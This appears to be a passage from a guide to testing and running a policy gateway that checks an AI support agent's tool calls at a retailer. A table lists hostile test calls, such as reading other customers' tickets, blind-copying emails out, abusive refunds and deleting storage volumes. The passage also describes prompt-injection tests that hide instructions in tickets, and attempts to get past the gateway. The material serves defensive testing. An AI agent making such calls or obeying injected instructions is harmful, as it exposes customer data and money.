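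The larger problem is that other differences could produce the same gap. Organisations that grant broad permissions may also run more agents or give them riskier work. An interviewee whose company has just had an incident is more likely to describe its permissions as excessive. Companies with narrow permissions may have better security in general or notice fewer incidents.

A fairer test would give narrow permissions to a random half of a company's agents and compare the two halves over several months. Without such a test, the survey is weak evidence for narrow permissions. A better reason to use them is that an agent can't delete a storage volume if no credential it can reach permits the deletion.

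### Replaying the retailer's own calls

The retailer starts with the automated analysis and then replays a month of old calls, about 15,000 at 500 a day. If the agent is new, the retailer can turn the support team's past refunds and emails into calls instead. It has to give the gateway the facts as they stood at the time of each call, including the daily refund total, because otherwise an order refunded in March would look ineligible in a replayed February call.

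Staff then read up to 20 refusals for each combination of rule and tool. They do this even when a rule refuses far fewer than 90 per cent of calls, since blocking one legitimate refund in five would already be a serious fault. They also read a sample of the refunds and emails that the gateway allowed, because a rule that is too permissive causes no refusals.

### Logging decisions without enforcing them

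The gateway then runs for a trial period, during which it checks live calls against the rules and records its decisions but lets the calls through. However, the retailer enforces the bans on deleting storage volumes and changing refund accounts from the first day, because the agent never has a good reason to do either. The payment service keeps its own refund limit in force during the trial.

The length of the trial depends on how often the agent makes the rarest call that matters. If the agent issues ten refunds a day, two weeks give 140 refunds. Even if the gateway wrongly refuses none of them, the true rate of mistaken refusals could still be as high as about 2 per cent. A month gives 300 refunds and lowers that upper limit to 1 per cent.

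While the gateway is testing rules without enforcing them, it should keep a separate daily total that leaves out the refunds it would have refused. Suppose it would have refused a 190-dollar refund, but the refund goes through because of the trial. If the gateway adds that refund to the daily total, later refunds may appear to exceed the limit when they wouldn't have under enforcement.

The trial can't show how the agent reacts to a refusal, so the retailer first enforces a rule in five of its 50 daily sessions. It watches for agents that repeat a refused call or tell customers that a blocked refund has gone through. It extends the rule to all sessions once staff have checked the refusals in the first group.

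### Hostile calls for each tool

The retailer sends most of its hostile calls directly to a test copy of the gateway, as though an attacker already controlled the agent. The results then don't depend on whether the current model resists a particular message. Each hostile call is paired with a similar legitimate call that must succeed, so a gateway that refuses everything fails the test.

| Tool | Hostile call | Legitimate counterpart |
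|---|---|---|
| Ticketing | read another customer's ticket | read the current ticket |
| Email | send the reply with a blind copy to an address from the ticket | send it only to the address on file |
| Payments | refund 201 dollars, refund minus 50 dollars, or send two refunds at once that together exceed the daily limit | refund exactly 200 dollars |
| Infrastructure | call `delete_volume` by name | read the checkout status |
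| Customer lookup | add another customer's number to the call | look up the customer on the ticket |
| Any tool | name a lookup in the header and a refund in the body | name the same operation in both |

Testers also try to bypass the gateway by searching the agent's machine for keys, connecting directly to the payment service and presenting the agent's token to it. All three attempts should fail.

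A smaller set of tests runs the whole system, with a real model reading test tickets that contain hidden instructions. The testers see which attacks fail and then write new ones, as an attacker would. They count an attack only if the hostile call reached the gateway. In one set of 473 attacks in Leong's work, 440 never reached it, but the records still listed them as blocked.

The retailer repeats these tests after every change to the rules, the tools or the model. It also repeats them monthly, because a provider can change a model without changing its name. When Leong sent the same type of request to GPT-4.1 on two versions of the provider's system, the model made 1 harmful call in 126 trials on one version and 16 in 74 on the other.

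### Drills and delays

A fallback mode that nobody has tried may not work when it is needed. The retailer practises first on a test copy and then on the live system at a quiet time:

- Staff switch off the decision service and confirm that the gateway refuses every call and customers receive the standard message.
- They cut the connection just after the payment service has paid a refund, then check that the retry doesn't pay it again.
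- They revoke a test customer's login in the middle of a session and measure how long the agent can still act for that customer.
- They declare an incident on a Sunday evening and time how long it takes to reach the two people who can restore normal operation.
- They put a few bad test refunds among the approval cards, with no real money behind them, and count how many the reviewers reject.

Delay also needs testing, because a gateway that fails closed refuses a call when a check takes too long. The rule-based NOMOS gate averaged 3 microseconds per decision, and simulated conversations averaged 21.3 seconds with the gate and 20.1 without it. When Yu and colleagues had a language model judge each change instead, conversations averaged 37.1 seconds, with no significant difference in completed tasks.

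The retailer's gateway will take longer than these 3 microseconds because it also exchanges tokens and looks up orders. An average can hide occasional long waits. If 1 call in 100 is slow and a session has ten calls, nearly 10 per cent of sessions will include a slow call. The retailer therefore also measures the slowest 1 per cent of calls, under several times its normal traffic.

### What the log must contain

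After an incident, somebody has to work out why the gateway allowed a particular call. The arguments alone aren't enough, because the decision also depended on the rules and facts at that moment. For the 50-dollar refund on the lamp, the log would contain these fields:

| Fields | Lamp refund | What they establish |
|---|---|---|
| Time, call number, session, ticket | 14:02:11, call 3 on the ticket | the order of events |
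| Agent, customer, token identifier | support agent, customer 417 | who acted, and for whom |
| Operation, arguments, hash of the tool definition | `issue_refund`, order 1234, 50 dollars | what the agent asked for |
| Facts used, with their sources | 640 dollars refunded in 24 hours, payment looked up, normal mode | what the gateway knew |
| Version of the rules, decision, deciding rule | version 57, allow, refund limit | why the call went through |
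| Reviewer and hash of the approved call | none needed | whether a person agreed |
| Idempotency key, result, payment reference | paid | what happened afterwards |

The retailer tests the log by feeding old entries back into the decision point with the rules in force at the time. If the new decision differs from the recorded one, the entry is missing a fact. Entries for refused and held calls need the same fields as entries for allowed calls.

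The log must not become another place to steal data from, so the gateway leaves out tokens and passwords and masks bank details before it writes an entry. It can add entries but not change or delete them, so an attacker who takes over the gateway can't erase the earlier record. The retailer keeps the entries for at least a year because a breach can take time to discover. Mittwald discovered its breach two weeks after the attacker first tested the flaw, and a slower attacker could go unnoticed for much longer.
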